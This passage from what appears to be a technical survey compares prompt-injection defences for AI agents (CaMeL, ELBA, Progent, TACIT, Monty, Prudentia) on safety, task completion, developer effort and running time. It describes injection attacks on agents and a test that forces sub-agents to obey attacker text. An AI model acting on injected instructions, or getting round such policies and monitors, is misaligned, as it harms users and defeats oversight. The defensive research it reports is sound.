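Many of the suite's 1,296 attacks can be resisted without labels. Garby and colleagues found that 97 of the 144 pairs need a tool that the user's task does not require, such as a payment tool when the user only wants a summary of recent transactions. A planner that never reads the attacker's text will normally resist those attacks without labels. Even on the other 47 pairs, CaMeL resisted 279 of 282 attacks with its policies off.

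### Standard attacks against recent models

In the Slack comparison, ELBA and CaMeL resisted all 105 injections with every model and every wording, whether their policies were on or off. ELBA without policies has no rule about who may receive a message or where its text came from, so its perfect score mainly reflects the models' own resistance.

Older and smaller models are still vulnerable to the same attacks. In *Kairos*, the most common AgentDojo attack succeeded against an unprotected agent in 47.0% of cases on GPT-4.1, 32.3% on Llama-3.3-70B and 28.3% on Qwen3.6-35B. Attacks that adapt to their target are also harder to resist. Zhou and colleagues cite GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attacker, which consistently got past GPT-5.5's defences. A model's success against a fixed attack text is therefore no reason to expect that a policy would stop an attack the model failed to resist.

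### ELBA with sub-agents that obey the attacker

To test the policies themselves, Zhou and colleagues made the models give way. They changed ELBA's code so that whenever a sub-agent's data contained the marker of an AgentDojo injection, the sub-agent received only the data, without a task description. The attacker's text thus became its whole task. They ran the 105 attack pairs seven times with each model, making 735 runs:

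| Model | Injections resisted, policies on | Injections resisted, policies off | Tasks done, policies on | Tasks done, policies off |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 | 351 | 523 |
| Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 | 312 | 557 |
| GPT 5.4 | 735 | 621 | 338 | 558 |
| Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 | 294 | 494 |

With policies enabled, AgentDojo wrongly scored 29 of the 2,940 runs as successful attacks because it counts a visit to a certain web address as a success. Zhou and colleagues reviewed all 29, found no violations, and counted them as resisted attacks.

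The policies stopped 894 attacks that would otherwise have succeeded, but they also reduced the number of completed tasks from 2,132 to 1,295. The attacks did not cause that loss, since ELBA with policies on completed about 44% of tasks in this test, 45% under the ordinary attacks and 44% with no attacker present. Its policies block the same legitimate actions in all three situations, so users would complete fewer tasks even if attacks were rare.

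Zhou and colleagues ran this test only on ELBA. They expect CaMeL to resist such attacks too, because its tool calls do not depend on data. But data can still supply the arguments, so an equivalent test of CaMeL would make its quarantined model give the attacker's answer to every question.

### Policy strictness

Turning policies on changes the results more than switching between most of these systems does. In the Slack comparison with no attacks present, ELBA's completed tasks across the four models fell from 64 to 37, and CaMeL's fell from 61 to 20. In the banking comparison, CaMeL's completed runs fell from 66 to 36 out of 96. The model and the planning method stayed the same in each comparison of policies on and off.

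*Kairos* provides an even cleaner test because it keeps the same monitor in the same place and changes only how it handles uncertain actions. Normally, a second model judges any action that the written policy doesn't settle. When the monitor instead refused all such actions, the share of tasks completed when there were no attacks fell from 85.1% to 42.7%. The change in attack success was within the variation expected between runs.

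Policy also explains part of Randori's advantage over CaMeL. With MiMo, Randori completed 31 of 48 unattacked runs, while CaMeL completed 18 with policies on. Randori completed 26 when its planner could not endorse data, so endorsement accounts for 5 of the 13 additional runs. Some of the other 8 may also reflect policy, because Randori implements only some of CaMeL's rules. ELBA's policies, which lower an agent's privileges whenever it reads untrusted data, also differ from CaMeL's.

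These benchmarks also make refusals look more disruptive than they would be in practice. A user could approve a refused payment, but the runs in *Kairos*, for example, included no user who could do so. Zhou and colleagues point out that a strict check can still save users time, since they need to review only the actions it refuses.

### Planning before or after reading data

The Slack results with policies off are the best evidence on planning style, since ELBA can plan as it reads and CaMeL cannot. ELBA completed only 3 more of the 84 unattacked runs than CaMeL, and with GPT 5.4, CaMeL did slightly better both with and without attacks. Reading data first seems to have helped Sonnet 5 and Opus 4.7 under attack, although ELBA and CaMeL also use different prompts and languages.

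AgentDojo understates this effect because many of its tasks suit advance planning. *Kairos* reproduces results from AgentDyn, whose tasks do not. In those results, an unprotected GPT-4o agent completed 53.3% of the tasks when there were no attacks, but an agent with the guard library Progent completed only 6.7%. *Kairos* left CaMeL out of this test because CaMeL fixes its program before the task begins. None of the three comparisons with CaMeL used AgentDyn.

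### Guard library against interpreter

Two further studies ran Progent and CaMeL in a shared test setup, which comes closest to comparing a guard library with an interpreter. *Kairos* used three agent models, with one run of each configuration and CaMeL's policies on:

| Agent model | Measure | No defence | Progent | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | Attacks that succeeded | 47.0% | 11.5% | 0.2% |
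| GPT-4.1 | Tasks done, no attack | 82.7% | 78.2% | 38.0% |
| Qwen3.6-35B | Attacks that succeeded | 28.3% | 5.4% | 0.4% |
| Qwen3.6-35B | Tasks done, no attack | 87.0% | 82.1% | 40.4% |
| Llama-3.3-70B | Attacks that succeeded | 32.3% | 8.0% | 0.0% |
| Llama-3.3-70B | Tasks done, no attack | 29.8% | 31.8% | 26.5% |

*SecureClaw* (Ma and Schmid, 2026) found the same pattern with adapted versions of both systems. Progent let through 24 of 629 attacks and completed 59 of 97 tasks run without an attack. CaMeL let through no attacks and completed 29 of the tasks.

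CaMeL was clearly safer and Progent more useful, but they differ in more than where they check policy. CaMeL also plans in advance and uses stricter rules about where data came from. If Progent had a rule that refused every recipient the user hadn't named, it would stop more attacks and complete fewer tasks while still being a guard library.

The choice of model can matter as much as the choice of system. With Llama, even the unprotected agent completed few tasks, so CaMeL reduced the number only slightly. CaMeL failed almost completely on Travel with Gemini, and it did so again with Llama in *Kairos*, where it completed 0.7% of tasks in the attacked Travel runs, compared with 33.6% with GPT-4.1 and 42.9% with Qwen. CaMeL's planner depends heavily on the model's ability to write a correct program before reading any data.

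Results for a single system also vary between studies. In Progent's own evaluation with GPT-4o, 1.0% of attacks succeeded, compared with 11.5% in *Kairos* with GPT-4.1 and 3.8% in Ma and Schmid's tests. According to *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (2026), the share of tasks completed without attacks in Progent's evaluation fell only from 79.4% to 76.3%. Comparing two systems using scores from different papers could easily reverse their order.

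### Conditions for a fair test

A fair comparison would change one thing at a time. To measure the effect of the enforcement level, researchers would need to keep these the same:

- **The models.** Systems with two models should use the same ones in both roles. *ToolFence* (2026) gives CaMeL's planner and its quarantined model the same underlying model so that neither role benefits from a stronger one.
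- **The tool descriptions.** Every system should receive the result formats that CaMeL's planner needs in advance. Peters-Gill and colleagues note that CaMeL's original evaluation added them too.
- **The policy.** Each system should forbid the same flows and allow the same exceptions. Zhou and colleagues suggest using an existing library such as LIO to standardise policies across agents. Somebody should also write the policy without seeing the test tasks, since *Agent-Sentry* (2026) observes that the policies for Progent and CaMeL encode the benchmark's full list of tools and data formats.
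- **The response to a refusal.** Either every system can ask a simulated user for approval, or none can.
- **The tasks and scoring.** All systems need the same benchmark version and the same corrections for false positives. Each task needs several runs, and the confidence intervals should allow for attack pairs that share a user task.

A separate comparison should test an agent that plans in advance against one that plans as it reads, with both under the same policy. Both agents should attempt some tasks that can be planned in advance and some that cannot.

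The attacks should include a version of Zhou and colleagues' forced test for each system, because a weak policy can look secure when the model is cautious. They should also include code that attempts to bypass the tools, which AgentDojo cannot test with its simulated tools. Even *Kairos*, whose monitor is meant to catch such code, had to translate each simulated call into an event before the monitor could check it.

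## Developer effort and running time

A team that moves a check out of the model has to write and maintain it, and the agent has to wait for it to run. The amount of work depends on the level:

| Where the check sits | What the team writes first | What it maintains |
|---|---|---|
| Guard library | A few lines around the tools, and rules for each tool | Rules, whenever tools or tasks change |
| Interpreter | A parser, an evaluator and library modules, unless one exists | Support for new language features and missing libraries |
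| Typed or capability language | A shared library and a typed interface for each set of tools | The interfaces, and compatibility with new compiler versions |
| Sandbox | Settings for directories, hosts and resources | Settings, whenever the agent needs a new program |

### Rules and sandbox settings

Library-level enforcement is the easiest kind to add to an existing agent. Developers can attach Progent, a guard library by Shi and colleagues, by wrapping a list of tools, adding middleware to an agent framework, or starting a proxy and changing one address in the agent's settings. Most of the remaining work is writing rules.

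A sandbox also requires little from its users, but much more from its developers. In *From Translation to Superset*, Wang and Sengupta (2026) counted 4,603 lines of Rust in Codex CLI's policy engine, which compares commands with rules, and 13,036 in its sandbox module. The sandbox module covers macOS, Linux and Windows, which each have different isolation mechanisms.

Most teams can use an existing sandbox. *Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) describes a Linux sandbox of about 7,000 lines of code that combines Landlock with seccomp and needs no administrator rights. Wang and Zheng ran unmodified `python3`, `make`, `node` and `pytest` in it after granting each program access to its temporary directories. They had not yet studied less common tools systematically, and Sandlock does not start on Linux versions before 6.12.

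### Missing libraries

A team that adopts Monty does not have to write an interpreter, but its agents can use only the parts of Python that Pydantic has rebuilt. In *pydantic-monty investigation*, Willison (2026) had Claude Code review a May release of Monty, and the review found that unsupported features generally fail with a structured error.

Third-party packages are a bigger problem, because the developer has to provide them through host functions. Pydantic built an agent that collects prices from the websites of model providers, whose pages are too long for a model to read. The agent's program needed Beautiful Soup, a library for searching web pages, so the developers wrote a class with matching methods, such as `find` and `select`. For the browser library Playwright, they kept the real browser pages on the host, and the program used objects that referred to them by number. This is practical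 for a few methods, but a data analysis library such as pandas has hundreds.

CPython compiled to WebAssembly avoids much of this work. According to Pydantic's *Comparison to Alternatives*, it supports almost the whole language and can load packages written purely in Python. Packages that contain C code, including many for data analysis, need a special build.

### Typed interfaces and porting

TACIT uses the standard Scala compiler, whereas CaMeL needs its own Python interpreter. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* puts TACIT's shared code at about 1,000 lines, including the capability library, the `Classified` wrapper and the connection to the trusted model. Only this shared code requires knowledge of capture checking. Each new domain also needs a facade, a set of typed methods that call the existing tools. The facades for an airline and a retailer are each a few hundred lines, about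 as long as the JSON tool descriptions they replaced. A model can draft a facade from such descriptions for a person to review.

These figures leave out most of the policy, because somebody still has to design types such as the one for trusted addresses.

ELBA requires more porting because its guarantee covers only code written in Haskell. Wang and Sengupta's work suggests that models can now do much of this kind of porting. They had a model translate Codex from Rust into Python, with an intensive phase of three days in March 2026. The original completed 38 of the 80 command-line tasks in Terminal-Bench, and the translation completed 34.

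Security code is harder to port with confidence. Wang and Sengupta used benchmark scores to find mistakes that their unit tests had missed, such as a malformed tool request that the model's provider always rejected. That method finds errors that stop an agent from working, but not errors that let a forbidden command through, because those do not lower the score. Both versions ran Terminal-Bench with unrestricted access, so those results provide no evidence that the translated sandbox works.

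### Models writing Scala and Haskell

Capture checking is rare in training data, so models might be expected to struggle with it. Odersky and colleagues tested this on τ²-bench's customer service tasks. Each model completed the tasks once with ordinary tool calls and once by writing typed Scala, without any worked examples. The scores are the share of tasks completed, averaged over ten runs of each task:

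| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, Scala | Retail, tool calls | Retail, Scala |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

The Scala agent did better in all six comparisons. Odersky and colleagues credit Scala's structured return types and the compiler's error messages. However, the comparison does not isolate the effect of these features, because the Scala agent writes programs while the other agent makes separate calls. An agent writing untyped Python might have gained just as much.

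On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues that an agent has to fix, MiniMax M2.5 resolved 43.3% with ordinary tools and 41.7% through TACIT, a difference of five issues. The researchers suspect that coding tasks depend more on habits of using the shell, which are awkward to express through TACIT's library.

On τ²-bench, the compiler rejected between 0.32% and 7.93% of snippets, depending on the model and domain, and five of the six rates were below 1.6%. Rejected snippets needed between 1.06 and 1.39 retries on average. Common mistakes included mishandling values that might be null and forgetting to escape a dollar sign in text, neither of which is related to security.

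Models also wrote Haskell programs for ELBA with few retries. Zhou and colleagues recorded an average of 0.13 retries per run on AgentDojo, ranging from 0.05 with Opus 4.7 to 0.19 with GPT 5.4. Retries took 3.4% of the running time. ELBA stopped 7 of 2,688 runs because the model repeatedly failed to produce a program of the right type. These rates are not directly comparable with TACIT's because one ELBA run can contain several generated programs.

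### Debugging a refusal

A compiler error points to a line of code, and a guard library can return a reason for its refusal. Operating system sandboxes usually give the program less information. When a program in Sandlock starts too many processes, it receives `EAGAIN`, the same error code that Linux uses for an ordinary shortage of resources. The model may then try to fix a fault that does not exist.

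Even a clear refusal does not help if the model cannot infer what the policy would allow. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) found that in most failed runs the agent kept attempting actions the policy had already rejected.

### Approval fatigue

Systems that ask the user too often cause approval fatigue, the habit of clicking yes without reading.

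The wording of a request can make this worse. In a typical example that Zhou and colleagues give from Claude Code, a single command enters a deeply nested directory, changes a timeout in a settings file, runs integration tests and saves the output under today's date. The user has to approve or reject all of it as one string. Wang and Sengupta's port of Codex reduces repeated requests by applying each approval to equivalent commands until the end of the current turn.

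Kolluri and colleagues argue that earlier studies missed a benefit of strict checks because they ignored approvals. In practice, an agent without such checks often asks before every action with consequences, not only those that a policy would refuse. They propose two measures:

```
v(run)    =  number of calls in the run that fail the policy check
load      =  sum of v(run) over the tasks that the agent completed
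TCR@k     =  share of all tasks that the agent completed with v(run) ≤ k
```

TCR@0 is the task completion rate (TCR) when the agent gets no approvals, and TCR@∞ is the rate when it can get any number. Earlier evaluations typically compared a protected agent's TCR@0 with an unprotected agent's TCR@∞, which overstates how much protection lowers task completion for a user who would otherwise have to approve the unprotected agent's actions.

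### Prudentia

Kolluri and colleagues built Prudentia on top of FIDES to reduce approval requests. FIDES does not give its planning model the policy, so the model may read an untrusted variable unnecessarily and then need approval for everything it does next. Prudentia includes each tool's policy in the tool's description and gives the model its conversation's label. Before reading a variable, the model must give a reason and list the calls it plans to make afterwards. The enforcement code stays the same, so a bad plan can cause more approval requests but cannot bypass a check.

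Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse data instead of approving actions. Suppose an email contains a to-do list with ten items, each of which needs a sensitive tool call. If the agent reads the email as untrusted data, it needs ten approvals. If the user endorses the email first, the agent can do all ten tasks after one question.

The researchers ran four agents on AgentDojo without attacks and assumed that the user would approve every request. These are the results with OpenAI's o3-mini, averaged over five runs of the benchmark:

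| Agent | Approvals needed (load) | Tasks completed without approval (TCR@0) |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent that asks before every consequential call | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Ordinary agent with label checks | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | About 17 | 59.1% |

Most of the reduction in approvals with o3-mini came from labels and variables, which FIDES already had. Prudentia made a larger difference with o4-mini, where the approval load fell from 36.8 to 19.2. With that model, it completed slightly fewer tasks than FIDES, 73.2% against 75.7%. Since the load counts only completed tasks, a small part of the reduction may come from excluding tasks that Prudentia failed.

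On WASP, a benchmark for browser agents, the user's tasks were to comment on a post or upvote it. Prudentia needed no approvals because it could do both without reading the untrusted text. The ordinary agent needed an average of 1.0 to 3.7 approvals per task, depending on the model and website.

Endorsement is less useful for Bob's email because the agent sends only one message, so approving the email and endorsing the meeting notes each take one question. The approval request is easier to judge because it can show the address directly. To endorse the notes safely, the user would have to read them and notice the attacker's line. Endorsement saves the most effort when a short text leads to many actions, but a mistake then affects all of them.

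### Start-up time

An agent's running time has four main parts: starting the environment, waiting for the model, checking the code or its actions, and running the tools. Sandbox vendors usually advertise the startup time.

Pydantic published figures for Monty in early 2026 and again in the autumn. The early test ran one line of code that called one host function, which took 4.5 microseconds, or 4.8 milliseconds with type checking. Monty's later move to separate worker processes made it slower to start:

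| Environment | Start-up, early 2026 | Start-up, autumn 2026 | Ten more commands |
|---|---|---|---|
| Monty | 0.0045 ms | 0.8 ms, or 5 ms with a new worker pool | 0.4 ms |
| CPython in WebAssembly | Not included | 16 ms | 180 ms |
| Docker | 195 ms | 195 ms | 700 ms |
| Hosted sandbox (Daytona in autumn) | 1,000 ms or more | 1,500 ms | 400 ms |
| Pyodide (CPython in a JavaScript runtime) | 2,800 ms | 2,700 ms | 35 ms |

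All these figures come from Pydantic. The last column favours Monty because Monty keeps its variables between commands, while in the other tests each new command reran all the earlier ones. A developer could avoid most of that repetition in Docker by keeping one Python process open.

Wang and Zheng's measurement supports the figure for Docker. A trivial command took about 6 ms to run in Sandlock and roughly 260 ms in Docker, 44 times as long. *Kirin* (2026), which presents a system for running WebAssembly services, also supports WebAssembly's advantage. In its one-minute test, about 720 WebAssembly instances started, compared with 180 Docker containers.

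The evidence on hosted sandboxes conflicts. *The Rollout Infrastructure Tax in Coding-Agent Reinforcement Learning* (2026) found that a hosted sandbox started faster than a single container, while Pydantic found Daytona much slower than Docker. Pydantic could not reproduce Daytona's advertised start-up time of under 90 ms. Network delay explained at most 200 ms of the 1,500 ms Pydantic measured. The choice of provider and its settings may therefore matter more than the type of sandbox.

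### Packages

An empty environment starts quickly, but the agent's program may need large packages. *Readie* (Sivaraman, Li and colleagues, 2026) reports that a container whose image held pandas, PyTorch and the language toolkit NLTK took 17.4 seconds to become ready when the host had no copy of the image. Downloading and unpacking the layer with the packages took 15.0 of those seconds.

Importing a single package from an image already on the host took 1.0 to 2.8 seconds, even with compiled bytecode. Restoring a snapshot of a process that had already imported the package took 0.29 to 0.42 seconds. Readie, a system from the same study, keeps a small set of such snapshots and picks the one that should make each new program ready soonest.

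Preparing the right packages in advance is difficult because an agent decides what it needs as it works. In 30.8% of 6,833 recorded sessions, the agent imported new packages after its first turn. Monty avoids these imports by leaving out third-party packages. If the developer wraps a library on the host, the application can load it once and use it for every program.

### Checks and model calls

Checks that run as ordinary code are fast. In Wang and Sengupta's port, comparing a command with five rules took 0.001 ms, and handling a tool call with its approval step took 0.03 ms. A complete shell command took 3.5 ms, mostly to start the shell and collect its output. The researchers estimate that a model call takes 1 to 10 seconds, so a guard that consults a second model would take thousands of times longer than one that applies rules.

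Slow run-time checks matter little for short scripts. Even if they slowed a script as much as SASI slowed its worst test program, a 10 ms script would take about 36 ms. Compilation takes longer, but Scala checks a typical snippet in less than a second once the JVM has warmed up.

Designs that need fewer model calls usually finish sooner because model calls are slow. Pydantic asked an agent to compare the weather in London and Paris. With ordinary tool calls, Claude Sonnet 4.5 needed four model calls and 12.2 seconds. When it wrote a program for Monty, it needed two calls and 9.1 seconds. Halving the number of calls saved only 25% of the time because writing a program takes longer than choosing a tool.

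ELBA took about three times as long as CaMeL on AgentDojo, mainly because its sub-agents require extra model calls. But on Zhou and colleagues' bibliography tasks, an ordinary tool-calling agent made about four times as many model calls as ELBA and used 65 times as many input tokens.

### A ten-call task

In this example, a task needs ten sequential tool calls that take 0.2 seconds each. Pydantic's weather test suggests that a model call takes about 3 seconds to choose a tool or write the final answer, and about 6 seconds to write a program. CaMeL also asks its quarantined model two questions, as for Bob's email, at an assumed 3 seconds each. CaMeL's program produces the final answer without another model call. CaMeL's labels are assumed to take 10 ms, and ELBA's total is estimated at three times CaMeL's.

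| Design | Start-up | Model calls | Checks | Tools | Total |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Guard library, one call at a time | None | 11 × 3 s = 33 s | 0.3 ms | 2 s | 35 s |
| New Docker container for each call | 10 × 195 ms = 1.95 s | 33 s | Negligible | 2 s | 37 s |
| Monty with guarded host functions | 5 ms | 6 s + 3 s = 9 s | About 5 ms | 2 s | 11 s |
| TACIT, server already running | None | 9 s | Up to 1 s | 2 s | Up to 12 s |
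| CaMeL | Negligible | 6 s + 2 × 3 s = 12 s | 10 ms | 2 s | 14 s |
| ELBA | Negligible | About 40 s, including checks | Included | 2 s | About 42 s |

Model calls take up most of the time in every row. With Monty, the task takes less than a third as long as with the guard library in the first row because the model writes one program instead of making ten separate choices. Moving the check does not explain the difference, since Monty's host functions could apply exactly the same rules as the library. At the highest retry rate on τ²-bench, rejected snippets would add an average of about 0.8 seconds to TACIT's total.

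Start-up can take most of the running time. If the agent writes a single program that needs the large image from Sivaraman and colleagues' test, and the host has no copy of it, start-up accounts for 61% of the total of 17.4 + 9 + 2 = 28.4 seconds. Faster models would also increase the share of time spent on the other steps. If model calls were ten times as fast, starting the Docker containers or compiling the Scala snippet would take about a quarter of the total in the design that uses that step.

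Waiting for the user's approval can take longer than any of this. If the user needs 15 seconds to read and approve each call, ten approvals add two and a half minutes. Endorsing the data once would reduce that to 15 seconds, if the user can read the data as quickly as a single call.
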